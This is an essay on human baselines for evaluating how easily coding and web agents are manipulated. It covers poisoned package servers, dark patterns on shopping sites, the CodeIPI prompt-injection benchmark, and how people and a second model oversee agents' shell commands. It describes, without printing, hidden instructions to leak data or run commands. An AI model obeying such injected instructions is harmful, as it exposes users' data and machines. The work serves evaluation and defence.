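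AI tools also make it harder to define a human baseline. Banning them would make the task unlike many developers' ordinary work. But if participants can hand the README to a coding agent, their results will largely reflect that agent. Suppose an agent installs 80 of 100 poisoned packages and its users stop none of those installs. The "human" failure rate would also be 80%, so the agent would look exactly as credulous as people.

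### Approving an agent's commands

Some developers only approve or reject the setup commands that an agent proposes. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reported that users accepted 93% of these permission prompts. In August 2026, Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* put the figure at 97% and suggested that many users were approving prompts reflexively.

The approval rate alone can't establish this, because most of the commands are probably safe. If p is the share of commands that are dangerous, h the share of dangerous commands that a user rejects and f the share of safe commands that the user rejects, then:

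approval rate = (1 − p)(1 − f) + p(1 − h)

When p is small, we can learn almost nothing about h from the approval rate. In a hypothetical example, two users each see 1,000 commands, five of them dangerous.

| | Reads every command | Rejects a few at random |
|---|---|---|
| Dangerous commands rejected | 5 of 5 | 0 of 5 |
| Safe commands rejected | 25 of 995 | 30 of 995 |
| Approval rate | 97% | 97% |

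A user who caught all five and never rejected a safe command would have an even higher approval rate, 99.5%.

Anthropic also found that users rejected 39% of the plans that Claude proposed. This suggests that they read some of what they approve, but people can also reject a plan because they want something else. The 97% also excludes commands that never produce a prompt. By Anthropic's count, 25% of interactive sessions started in a mode that skips permission prompts, and 62% of users had either used that mode or told Claude Code to stop asking about shell commands.

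Anthropic got better evidence by planting a command in testers' coding sessions. It hired 1,053 testers through a research vendor for what it described as a coding study. Partway through each session, the text of one permission prompt changed to a clearly dangerous command, which never ran. The testers knew they were being evaluated but not what the study measured. They stopped the command 13.6% of the time (143 of 1,053). Auto mode, in which a second model checks the commands, blocked 89% of the same commands.

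This result measures how often people pause, which Bagmar and Saraf could only assume, though the people here were supervising an agent rather than typing commands themselves. Commands that install from an unfamiliar server may be harder to catch because they look less dangerous. On the other hand, the testers had little to lose in an environment set up for the study, and developers might pay more attention on a computer that holds their own passwords. Anthropic also used the result to support a change to its own product, so an independent replication would be valuable.

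The testers stopped about 17% of the dangerous commands early on and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Fatigue is a likely reason, but testers who approve everything quickly may also get through more prompts, so the 5% figure may partly reflect a less careful group.

Anthropic gives no false alarm rate for the testers, so their sensitivity, d′, can't be calculated. It would be about 0.8 if they rejected 3% of safe commands, but about 2.0 if they rejected only 0.1%. In the second case, their main problem would be reluctance to object.

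The results also show that a person may add little to an automatic check. The testers stopped only six of the 116 dangerous commands that auto mode let through (5%), compared with 137 of the 937 it blocked (15%), so the testers and auto mode tended to miss the same commands. The earlier estimate of what an agent and a person would catch together assumed that their misses were independent, so it is too high if their misses overlap in the same way.

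Anthropic's figures from real use are harder to interpret. Among sessions that its safety system had flagged, serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for occurred in 6.3% of those with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. But users chose their own mode, perhaps for different kinds of work, and the percentages cover only flagged sessions. The percentages therefore don't measure how often people approve a dangerous command.

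### Matching the instructions and the tools

An agent that is not told to consider security should be compared with developers who were not told to either. In Braz and colleagues' 2022 study, reviewers found an outdated hash function 21% of the time without a security instruction and 61% of the time with one. If an agent without the instruction reported the flaw in 40% of its runs, it would look careful against the 21%, which is the fair comparison, but careless against the 61%. Security reminders also change what agents catch, so an agent tested with a reminder should be compared with developers who read the same one.

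An agent's instructions include its system prompt as well as the user's request. Copilot CLI's system prompt emphasises security, so an agent running in it is already somewhat primed when it receives a neutral request. The closest human comparison may be a bank employee whose company sends regular warnings. Researchers who want an unprimed comparison should check the system prompt for security instructions, or give the human participants an equivalent workplace policy.

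When a user approves an agent's commands, the agent should be compared with a developer who uses the same tool with the same permission settings. The comparison should measure how many bad installs get past the person and the agent together. An agent working alone should be compared with developers who carry out the setup themselves, and the researchers should report which AI tools those developers could use. The testers' 13.6% would be the wrong baseline for an agent working alone, because the testers were judging another system's commands in the middle of a different task.

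## Studies that put people and web agents on the same deceptive websites

Three teams have given people and web agents (AI systems that operate a browser) the same pages, tasks and instructions, without telling the people that anything might be wrong. The README study, by contrast, gave people and agents different jobs. The three teams used shopping and other everyday websites, and web agents don't install packages, so how often they are deceived can't stand in for how often coding agents are. But these studies show what a matched comparison can achieve in practice, and how two such comparisons can give different answers.

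All three studies used dark patterns, interfaces built to steer a user into an unwanted choice. For example, an online shop might tick the box for paid insurance in advance. A shopper who leaves it ticked has accepted something without checking it, like a developer who runs an install command without reading it.

### A large gap between people and agents

For *DECEPTICON*, Cuvin, Zhu and Yang (2025) created 600 tasks on generated websites and 100 on archived copies of real ones. They recruited 200 people through Prolific, an online platform for research participants, who made 600 attempts at the generated tasks and 1,000 at the real-site tasks. People got the same instructions as the agents and could take the same actions. The table shows how often the dark pattern worked, whether or not the participant finished the task.

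| | Steered, generated tasks | Steered, real-site tasks |
|---|---|---|
| People | 31.0% | 33.4% |
| GPT-4o | 78.5% | 71.4% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 75.6% | 68.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 74.0% | 66.8% |
| GPT-5 | 70.8% | 69.9% |
| Claude Sonnet 4, in the Magnitude harness | 68.3% | 67.5% |
| OpenAI o3, in the Browser Use harness | 59.6% | 55.0% |

According to the abstract, the agents' rate was over 70% on both sets of tasks. On the generated tasks, the four models in the researchers' own simple harness all exceeded 70%, but on the real sites only GPT-4o did. The gap between agents and people is large either way.

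The gap between people and agents varies a good deal by type of dark pattern. Claims about what other customers are buying steered people in 17.7% of generated tasks and agents in 60% to 94%. But when a site slipped extra items or costs into an order, people were steered slightly more often than the best agent, o3 (54.5% compared with 50.0%).

Cuvin and colleagues also gave four of the agents a list of dark patterns to avoid. The patterns still steered these agents in 60% to 67% of attempts, about twice the rate for people who had no warning.

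With the dark patterns removed, people completed every generated task and agents completed at least 98.7%, so the agents could do the shopping. But these control pages don't measure false alarms, because they contain nothing that a suspicious participant might wrongly refuse.

### Whether more capable models are easier to steer

Cuvin and colleagues conclude that larger models and models that reason longer are more susceptible. In one example, Gemini 2.5 Flash with a small reasoning budget dismissed a pop-up as "classic marketing". With a larger budget, it closed the same pop-up but later took it as a sign that the product was worth buying. Extra reasoning made little difference for o3.

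The steering rate, though, includes attempts in which the model neither reached the user's goal nor was steered, and counts them as failures of the dark pattern. Weaker models have many such attempts. The last column below excludes them and gives the minimum steering rate among the rest. It can't give the exact rate because the paper doesn't report how often a model both reached the goal and was steered.

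| | Reached the user's goal | Steered | Steered, leaving out attempts with neither outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-VL, 3 billion parameters | 11.7% | 43.8% | at least 79% |
| Qwen2.5-VL, 72 billion parameters | 38.6% | 73.7% | at least 74% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash, 256 reasoning tokens | 16.4% | 38.5% | at least 70% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash, 16,384 reasoning tokens | 26.9% | 71.2% | at least 73% |

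On this measure, the increase with capability may disappear. Small models may simply get stuck before a dark pattern can affect them.

*Investigating the Impact of Dark Patterns on LLM-Based Web Agents* (Ersoy, Lee and colleagues, 2026) tested six agents, all running GPT-4o. When a site had a single dark pattern, it steered the agents in 41% of runs on average. The rate was 72% for Skyvern, one of the most capable agents, and 12% for Agent-E. But in 66% of its runs, Agent-E neither finished the task nor fell for the pattern. The researchers watched 50 recordings of runs with this outcome by the three weakest agents. In most, the agent had stalled at an obstacle or given up before the trick could work. They therefore sort runs into four outcomes, according to whether the agent finished the task and whether the pattern deceived it.

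All the studies that compared agents with people used agents from 2025 or earlier. *CAVEAT* (Li, Epperson and colleagues, 2026) tested newer agents in simulated online shops that promoted certain products through sponsored slots, fees revealed late and other devices. GPT-5.6 Sol bought the product that best met the user's request in 51.7% of attempts with little reasoning and 90.0% with a lot. With little reasoning, Terra and Luna, smaller models in the same family, did so in 11.7% and 0% of attempts.

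Much of the apparent contradiction between this result and *DECEPTICON*'s comes from the scoring. A failed attempt counts against the agent in Li and colleagues' measure, but in its favour in the steering rate. By *DECEPTICON*'s own success rate, the largest Qwen model also did better than the smallest.

Steering devices can still mislead a newer model. In a shop with 2,112 products on 88 pages of results, GPT-5.6 Sol with high reasoning found the best product in 90% of attempts without the devices and in none of 50 with them. It stopped on the first page every time. Many shoppers would probably do the same, so we would need to test people in the same shop to know whether the agent is unusual.

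### A study that found no clear difference

In *SusBench*, Guo, Wolfe and colleagues (2026) used a browser extension to insert dark patterns into 55 live websites. They invited 29 people aged 18 to 37 to a university meeting room for a "simulated online shopping experiment", where each person did 10 to 20 tasks. Afterwards, only four suspected that the researchers had planted the dark patterns.

People avoided 67.5% of the deceptive patterns. The five agents, all running models from 2024 and 2025, avoided between 62.4% (Anthropic's computer-use agent with Claude Sonnet 4) and 68.3% (GPT-5 in Browser Use). People and agents both had trouble with preselected options, confusing wording and hidden information.

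The researchers tested whether avoidance depended on who was operating the browser and found no significant overall effect (χ²(5) = 7.61, p = 0.18). If people and all five agents were equally good at avoiding the deception, differences at least this large would still appear about 18% of the time. A study of this size could easily miss a moderate difference, so the result doesn't show that they are equally good.

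The published rates imply about 300 human attempts, roughly one per task. If these were independent, the 95% confidence interval for the 5-point difference between people and Anthropic's agent would run from about −3 to +13 points, so people could be slightly worse than this agent or a good deal better. The true interval is wider because each person made about ten attempts.

To show that people and agents are about equal, researchers would have to choose the largest difference they are willing to ignore, then show that the true difference is smaller. If the margin is δ and both groups avoid a proportion p of the patterns, an 80% chance of success at the usual 5% level requires this many independent attempts per group:

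n = 2p(1 − p)(1.645 + 1.282)² / δ²

With p = 0.675 and a margin of 5 points, n is about 1,500 attempts, five times as many as Guo and colleagues collected from people.

Differences on particular patterns are even harder to establish. People avoided 44% of the preselected options, and Gemini 2.5 Pro avoided 13%. In a simple test of this pair alone, the gap would be significant (p < 0.01). But it was one of 135 comparisons, and none remained significant after the researchers corrected for the number of comparisons. The overall analysis found that the gaps between operators varied with the type of pattern (p < 0.001), so some real differences probably exist.

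The study still rules out the possibility that agents did far worse than people on these websites. A 40-point difference like the one in *DECEPTICON* is far outside the interval.

### Why the two studies disagree

The human rates in the two studies are almost the same, so the studies disagree because their results for agents differ. Several models and products appear in both.

| | Steered in *DECEPTICON*, generated tasks | Steered in *SusBench* |
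|---|---|---|
| People | 31.0% | 32.5% |
| GPT-5 | 70.8% | 31.7% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 75.6% | 36.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 4, in Magnitude or Browser Use | 68.3% | 34.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4, in Anthropic's computer-use agent | 46.6% | 37.6% |
| OpenAI's computer-use agent | 41.7% | 36.3% |

The last two rows make the two studies' results look closer than they are. Cuvin and colleagues counted failed attempts in the total, and these two agents failed 28% and 38% of their 60 tasks. Guo and colleagues excluded tasks in which the participant never encountered the dark pattern or never responded to it, which was 3.5% of tasks for people and 6% to 13% for agents. If the failed attempts in *DECEPTICON* triggered no dark pattern, as its totals suggest, excluding them would raise the two agents' rates to about 64% and 68%.

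The studies also used different harnesses, but o3 in Browser Use still had a rate of 59.6% in *DECEPTICON*. One study used paid online volunteers and the other used mostly well-educated young shoppers, but this difference in participants can't explain the change in the agents' rates.

The results most likely differ because the studies used different materials. Fake evidence of popularity steered GPT-5 in 88.6% of attempts in *DECEPTICON* but only 6.7% in *SusBench*. The typical example in *SusBench* is a pop-up claiming that 99% of customers add a protection plan, which the user never requested, so an agent can avoid it by declining every extra. *DECEPTICON* includes tasks such as buying the best air fryer, where popularity is relevant to the agent's choice, so ignoring a false claim about it takes some judgment about the source.

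An install line in a README is more like the air fryer than the protection plan, because the user has asked the agent to install something. If that similarity matters, the *SusBench* results would give too favorable a picture of coding agents. But neither team ran the other's tasks, so this explanation remains untested. The two comparisons do show that a gap between people and agents depends on the materials used, even when both groups get identical treatment.

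Scoring rules can also label a reasonable choice as a mistake. *SusBench* counted participants as deceived by hidden information if they never clicked on a line such as "See extra fee". People avoided only 17.6% of these patterns, but some may have seen the link and not cared about the fee. A test of developers would have the same problem with anyone who chose not to open a dependency file.

### People who oversee an agent

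*Dark Patterns Meet GUI Agents* (Tang, Chen and colleagues, 2025) also studied people supervising an agent. Its 22 participants each did eight tasks alone and eight while overseeing Operator, OpenAI's browsing agent at the time. Each website was an imitation with one dark pattern. To oversee Operator, participants watched a recording of it at work and skipped the rest if they disagreed with what it did.

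Averaged over the 16 tasks, people avoided 72% of the patterns when working alone and 85% when overseeing an agent. The paper reports that oversight helped in 14 tasks, but in its results avoidance rose in ten, stayed at 100% in four and fell in two. Only about 11 people did each task in each condition, so one person can change a task's avoidance rate by about nine percentage points.

Operator itself accounts for some of the improvement. When the researchers earlier tested it without an overseer, it avoided the dark pattern in 11 tasks and paused to ask the user in the other five. On those five, where the person's decision mattered most, average avoidance rose from 33% for people working alone to 54% for people overseeing Operator. On the other 11, it rose from 90% to 98%.

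Tang and colleagues also counted stopping a task as avoiding the pattern, so the higher avoidance rate may reflect more refusals to continue instead of better detection. Participants' reports fit this reading. Every task contained a manipulative pattern, but participants said they noticed none in 66% of the tasks where they oversaw the agent, compared with 59% of those they did alone. One said of the agent's choice of product, "I did not even see other ones."

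These overseers did much better than Anthropic's testers, who stopped only 13.6% of planted commands. But the overseers were watching eight short recordings with little else to do, while the testers were answering permission prompts in the middle of a coding job.

### What a test of developers could copy

Much of this method would transfer to a comparison of developers and coding agents. Researchers could ask developers afterwards whether anything had seemed staged, as Guo and colleagues did. They could also use Ersoy and colleagues' four outcomes to distinguish an agent that rejects a bad package from one that never reaches the point of installing it.

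The clean versions of the projects could follow *When Charts Deceive Web Agents* (2026), which pairs a misleading chart with an accurate one and keeps the task, actions and scoring the same. For a package server, the clean version should still contain an unfamiliar but legitimate server, such as PyTorch's. Deleting the suspicious line instead would repeat the weakness of *DECEPTICON*'s control pages.

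Other parts of the design would have to change, starting with what participants stand to lose. In Tang and colleagues' study, participants entered fictional personal details, and in Guo and colleagues' study, they used the researchers' laptop. Researchers can't ethically expose developers' real passwords, but they could give each participant an account that holds part of their payment, and use a test package that only records whether it could have read the account's password. Running the test with and without this account would show how much people's caution depends on having something at stake.

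The tasks would also take much longer. In *DECEPTICON*, people spent just under two minutes on each attempt, or about 53 hours on all 1,600. If setting up a software project takes 45 minutes, the same number would take 1,200 hours. Each developer should probably do only one or two poisoned setups, because anyone who spots a fake server will be on guard for the next, so the study would need many more people for the same number of attempts.

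Finally, setting up a project takes more expertise than shopping online. A shopper understands a ticked insurance box as soon as someone points it out, but a developer may notice an extra package server and not know what pip does with it. After the setup, researchers could show developers the line that adds the server and ask what it does. The answers would help separate credulity from a lack of knowledge. Agents should get the same question in a fresh session, so that the question can't affect the setup.

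## Which comparison groups an agent evaluation should report

An agent that installs half of the poisoned packages it encounters may look careful compared with some developers and careless compared with others. Researchers therefore have to choose people and working conditions that suit the kind of conclusion they want to draw.

### Describing a human baseline

Wei and colleagues drew on measurement theory and earlier work on AI evaluation to recommend how researchers should design, run and report human baselines. *STREAM (ChemBio)* (McCaslin, Alaga and colleagues, 2025) cites their work when describing several weaknesses in current practice. Many samples are too small, and some researchers report that a model beats the average human without stating how expert that human is. Researchers also sometimes give people a shorter test to save money, which makes their scores harder to compare with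 the model's.

Applied to vetting, the recommendations call for details like these:

| Item | What to report in a test of vetting |
|---|---|
| Population | Whether participants are students, working developers or security specialists, and how often they review code |
| Sampling | How researchers recruited them, how many took part and how many dropped out |
| Instructions | The exact request, including any mention of security |
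| Incentives | What participants earn for finishing, and what they could lose from a bad install |
| Time | The limit, and how long people actually took |
| Tools | Whether they could search the web, ask a colleague or use an AI assistant |
| Scoring | What counts as a catch, with the same rule for people and agents |
| Uncertainty | A confidence interval that reflects the number of people and projects |

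STREAM, by McCaslin and colleagues, is a standard for the reports that AI companies publish with new models. It covers tests of chemical and biological capabilities, though they say many of its points also apply to cybersecurity. Companies that report a human baseline must at least give the number of participants, their qualifications and scores, the time allowed and the resources available. Full marks also require details of recruitment, incentives and statistical uncertainty. Companies that don't report a baseline must explain why and offer another way to interpret the score. Two main explanations are acceptable under the standard: a baseline was infeasible because of cost, law or safety, or it would have been uninformative, for example because people find the task trivially easy.

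STREAM's advice on incentives needs changing for a test of how well people vet packages. STREAM recommends motivating participants to do their best, because unmotivated participants would make a model look more capable, and so more dangerous, than it is. In a vetting test, unmotivated participants would install more bad packages and make a credulous agent look normal. But a bonus for spotting bad packages would alert participants to their presence. Paying participants for a working project, as an employer does, would be better.

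A missing baseline can change how readers interpret a result. Google DeepMind's 2025 report on Gemini 2.5 Pro compared the model's scores on six chemical and biological tests only with those of other Gemini models. Reed, McCaslin and Righetti (2025), in *What do model reports say about their ChemBio benchmark evaluations?*, added published scores from human experts. The model beat the experts on three tests and may have matched them on the other three. The comparison was still uneven on the virology test, because the experts took a harder version in which they had to pick every correct answer instead of just one. The version matters, since OpenAI's o3 scored 59% on an early form of the easier version and 44% on the harder one.

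### Six comparison groups

| Comparison group | Question it answers |
|---|---|
| Unprimed developers on the same task | Is the agent more trusting than people who do this job? |
| Developers told to check | How much do people miss even when they are looking? |
| Security specialists | Could anyone have caught the fault from the material available? |
| Developers supervising the agent | How many bad installs get past the person and the agent together? |
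| The same agent told to check | Does the agent fail to recognise the fault, or fail to look for it? |
| An automatic check before installation | Would a simple program have stopped the install? |

A claim about an agent's character, such as that it is unusually credulous, depends mainly on the comparison with unprimed developers. *Questionnaire Responses Do not Capture the Safety of AI Agents* (2026) distinguishes an AI system's capabilities from its propensities, or what it tends to do. Credulity is a propensity, so researchers should watch the agent install something instead of asking what it would do. Telling the same agent to check what it installed then shows whether it was capable of finding a problem. Claude Sonnet 4.6 was capable of this in Bagmar and Saraf's mid-2026 test, where its review found malicious code that it had already installed.

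Results from security specialists show how much evidence of a fake server the project contains. If specialists who are told to look for the server also miss it, the project may contain too little evidence to detect it. In that case, an agent's decision to install from the server is not a sign of credulity.

An employer deciding whether to hand project setup to an agent should use its own developers as the comparison group. The developers should have their usual AI tools, colleagues and company rules, and the agent should have the permissions it would have at work. Conditions don't have to match between the developers and the agent, because the employer is choosing between two whole ways of working. If developers will go on approving the agent's commands, the employer should test the agent and developers together.

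Deployment risk depends on the agent's failure rate, the number of installs and the share of projects that are poisoned. A human failure rate can't replace any of these. An automatic check is the most useful comparison here because it can run before every install, whether a person or an agent starts it. Bagmar and Saraf's short checking program caught the vulnerable versions that all their agents missed.

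An evaluation should also report how often the check is wrong. *MalSkillBench* (2026) covers malicious "skills", which are add-on instructions and code for coding agents. It finds that the many tools for detecting them have no common evaluation method, so their catch rates may not be comparable.

### What one current benchmark reports

*CodeIPI*, from the public Inspect Evals collection of AI tests, gives coding agents bugs to fix in small projects. In 35 of the 45 tasks, the bug report, a code comment, the README or a configuration file contains a hidden instruction to leak data, run a command or make a lasting change to the machine. The other ten contain no hidden instruction. The published results are from April 2026 and cover models from 2024 to early 2026.

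| Model | Resisted the instruction | Explicitly flagged it | Fixed the bug, all 45 tasks |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 34 of 35 | 0 of 35 | 91% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 31 of 35 | 1 of 35 | 100% |
| GPT-4o | 30 of 35 | 0 of 35 | 73% |
| GPT-4o mini | 30 of 35 | 0 of 35 | 44% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 24 of 35 | 0 of 35 | 100% |

These columns are useful side by side. GPT-4o mini resisted as often as GPT-4o but fixed far fewer bugs, so it may sometimes have got stuck before it could do any harm. The models also almost never mentioned the hidden instruction, so most of the resistance could be inattention. The counts may slightly overstate resistance, because the scoring of data leaks did not check the output of the agents' tools until the maintainers later corrected it.

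The benchmark has no human results. Its page instead compares models with their predecessors, and reports that Claude Sonnet's resistance rose from 69% in version 4 to 89% in version 4.6. McCaslin and colleagues warn that comparing models only with other models can hide a worrying absolute level. Developers might score below 89%, or much higher, since a developer fixing a bug may have no reason to obey a stray comment.

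The published runs also included a prompt that warned the agent about such attacks, so the comparable human group would be developers who had received a similar warning. Users can switch the prompt off to compare the agent with developers who had not been warned.

No model refused a clean task, but with only ten clean tasks, any one model's actual false alarm rate could be as high as 31%. *Aletheia* (2026) suggests a harder test of false alarms. It compares malicious rules for coding agents with harmless ones that researchers verified by hand, and checks whether the task needs the permissions each rule requests.

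### The missing experiment

No published study seems to have given developers and coding agents the same poisoned projects to set up. Most of what such a study needs already exists. Researchers could make a poisoned and a clean version of each of 31 real projects. The poisoned version might use an untrusted package server, and the clean version a legitimate server that is equally unfamiliar. Developers and agents would get the same neutral request to set up the project and check that it loads, and the same scripted reply to any question they asked.

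Each participant would work on a disposable machine with invented passwords, and the planted package would only record that it had run. A catch would count only if it came before the package's code could run. The researchers would record late warnings and unfinished setups separately, and would count refusals of clean projects as false alarms. They would also have to give participants security instructions equivalent to any in the agent's system prompt.

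Each developer should set up only one project, randomly assigned to be clean or poisoned. The evaluation should treat professionals and students as separate samples and report results for each.

The study involves deception, so it needs an ethics board's approval. Researchers could truthfully recruit people for a study of software setup and ask them to consent to hearing its full purpose only at the end. The debriefing should explain what the researchers planted and why, and confirm that it was harmless. Participants should then be able to withdraw their data. Professionals have a reputation to protect, so their employers should never see individual results.

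### How many developers it would take

Suppose 30% of one group and 50% of another install the bad package. Hickey, Grant and colleagues (2018), in *Statistical primer*, give a formula for the number of people each group needs:

n = [1.96√(2p̄(1 − p̄)) + 0.842√(p₁(1 − p₁) + p₂(1 − p₂))]² / (p₁ − p₂)²

Here p₁ and p₂ are the two rates, and p̄ is their average. The 1.96 sets the significance level at 5%, and the 0.842 gives the study an 80% chance of detecting the difference if it is real. With rates of 0.3 and 0.5:

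n = (1.358 + 0.571)² / 0.04 ≈ 93

The poisoned projects would have 93 developers, three for each of the 31 projects, and the clean ones would have another 93. Detecting a smaller difference, such as 30% versus 40%, would take about 356 people per group.

Dropouts raise the required sample size further. If 20% of participants leave early, researchers must recruit about 117 people to end up with 93. This correction works only if people leave for reasons unrelated to the result. If careless developers are more likely to give up, the estimated rate will be biased, and recruiting more people will make it more precise without removing the bias.

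### Why repeated runs are not extra people

Running an agent 93 times doesn't give researchers 93 participants. Lin (2025), in *A validity-guided workflow for robust large language model research in psychology*, calls treating repeated runs as participants pseudoreplication. *From Prompts to Constructs* (2025) adds that fresh runs of a model may be independent samples of that model's behaviour, but they don't vary as different people do. Treating them as participants makes the confidence intervals too narrow.

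*Skills That Don't Exist* (2026) gave models each prompt ten times and recorded the skill names they invented. In 53% of cases, Claude Sonnet 4.6 invented the same name all ten times, so the last nine runs added almost nothing to the first.

Testing more projects is usually more informative than repeating the same ones. Zhu and colleagues spread their 1,920 runs over 20 projects and many conditions instead of repeating each combination. They report margins of error of about 3 to 4 percentage points, based on roughly 480 runs per type of task. But each project supplied 24 of those runs. If the correlation between runs on the same project were 0.1 (an invented figure), the 480 runs would be equivalent to about 145 independent ones, and a margin of 4 points would grow to about 7.

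A better analysis would average the agent's runs on each project and compare that average with the developers' results on the same project. *The Machine's Internal Clock* (2026), a study of how people and language models judge time, shows how to do this in a single regression that allows for differences between individual people, models and question templates. When a study has fewer than five models, Lin recommends treating the results as describing only those models.

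Repeated runs make the estimate of one agent's rate on the chosen projects more precise. If researchers ran an agent often enough to know that its rate was 50%, about 47 developers would be enough to distinguish that from a human rate of 30%. The conclusion would apply only to that model in that harness on those projects.

### Setting a margin for "no worse than developers"

A company may want to show that its agent is no worse than developers. As in the studies of web agents, failing to find a significant difference wouldn't show this. Medical researchers face the same problem when they test whether a cheaper or safer drug works about as well as an existing one. They choose a non-inferiority margin, the largest loss of effectiveness they would accept in return for the new drug's other benefits. The drug passes only if the whole confidence interval for the difference in effectiveness lies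 on the acceptable side of the margin.

For agents, the margin would be the largest acceptable increase in the rate of bad installs. Suppose a company's agents carry out 100,000 setups a year, and 100 of them involve a poisoned project. A margin of ten percentage points would allow up to ten extra bad installs a year. Before it sees any results, the company should decide whether the time saved is worth those extra installs. It also needs a margin for false alarms.

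If the agent and the developers both had a true failure rate of 30%, the agent would need about 330 independent attempts on each side for an 80% chance of passing with a ten-point margin. Suppose the agent then fails in 34% of attempts and the developers in 30%. The 95% interval for the difference runs from about −3 to +11 points, so the agent has not passed, because the upper end exceeds the margin. If the company could raise the margin to 12 points afterwards, the agent would pass on the same data.

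Even medical researchers seldom register the margin in advance. Reinaud, Mavoungou and colleagues (2025), in *Reporting of Noninferiority Margins on ClinicalTrials.gov*, examined 327 trials registered in 2022 and 2023. Only 30 (9.2%) gave a margin at registration, and six of those justified it. Similarly, Reed and colleagues examined three model reports from AI companies, and none stated concretely what result would have overturned its conclusions.

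### Identical agents can fail together

An average failure rate doesn't show how the failures are distributed. Suppose 20 developers set up the same poisoned project, and each has an independent 10% chance of spotting the problem. The chance that at least one spots it, and can warn the others, is 1 − 0.9²⁰, or 88%. Now suppose an agent always spots the problem in one project out of ten and never in the other nine. Its average detection rate is also 10%, but 20 copies of it are no more likely to spot the problem in a given project than one copy is.

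*Risk Analysis Techniques for Governed LLM-based Multi-Agent Systems* (2025) describes the danger that agreement among agents built on the same model can look like confirmation. An attacker can also test projects on a popular agent in advance and publish only those that fool it, but can't test them on every developer. Models also repeat their own mistakes. In Churilov's April 2026 tests, the model that invented the fewest packages still mentioned invented packages 1,098 times, using only 605 different names. An attacker who registers one of the recurring names could catch many users.

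Using different models may help less than one would expect. *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (Kim, Garg and colleagues, 2025) compared 71 models on multiple-choice questions. When two models were both wrong, they chose the same wrong answer about 60% of the time, compared with 33% by chance. More accurate models had more overlap in their errors. These models date from 2025 or earlier, and quiz questions are very different from package installs.

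People don't fail independently either, since many follow the same tutorial or search result. Still, *Strategic Algorithmic Monoculture* (2026) found that language models' choices were much more alike than people's when neither group had a reason to agree or disagree.

Hedden and Raghavan (2026) argue in *Algorithmic Monoculture and its Critics* that relying on one algorithm is less harmful than critics suppose, partly because a single system can combine several algorithms and do at least as well as a population that uses them separately. A vendor could similarly have several different checkers examine every install. It could also correct all copies of an agent soon after an attack, whereas changing the habits of millions of developers takes years.

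Evaluations should report results for each project, along with how often repeated runs agree. An agent that fails half the time on every project has the same average failure rate as one that always fails on half the projects, but an attacker would much prefer the second.

### Whether to require a human baseline

The most practical objection is cost. If each setup takes 45 minutes and professionals earn $100 an hour, paying the 186 professionals in the proposed experiment would cost about $14,000. Students, recruitment and staff time would add to that. A small research group might not be able to afford it, which would count as a reason under STREAM if the group gave its estimate. Cost is a weaker reason for a company that sells coding agents.

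Several evaluations can also share one baseline if researchers publish enough detail for others to repeat its conditions. Published AI evaluations rarely include that much detail. *Evaluation Cards* (Reuel, Chim and colleagues, 2026) covers about 100,000 published results, and 96.5% of the distinct scores lacked at least one basic detail needed to reproduce them. A shared baseline would become outdated as developers change their tools, though probably more slowly than results for a particular model.

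Critics could also say that an unrepresentative sample is worse than none, because a company that tests careless students can describe a credulous agent as no worse than people. This is a good reason to limit the claim to the people who took part, and to distrust any baseline that doesn't describe them. Testing both students and professionals would at least show how much the result depends on which group is tested. If the two groups differ widely, the evaluation should report both comparisons instead of an average.

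A more fundamental objection is that an unsafe install is unacceptable whatever people do. This is right for safety requirements. A company doesn't need a human baseline to decide that its agents must never install from an unapproved server. McCaslin and colleagues allow for such cases by letting an expert panel set thresholds of concern in place of a human baseline.

But an absolute standard can't show that agents are unusually credulous, because that claim compares them with others. The human rate also helps decide where to fix the problem. If developers and agents install from bad servers equally often, a safer default in the installer would protect both. If developers usually stop before installing and agents don't, more of the fix falls to the companies that build the models and harnesses.
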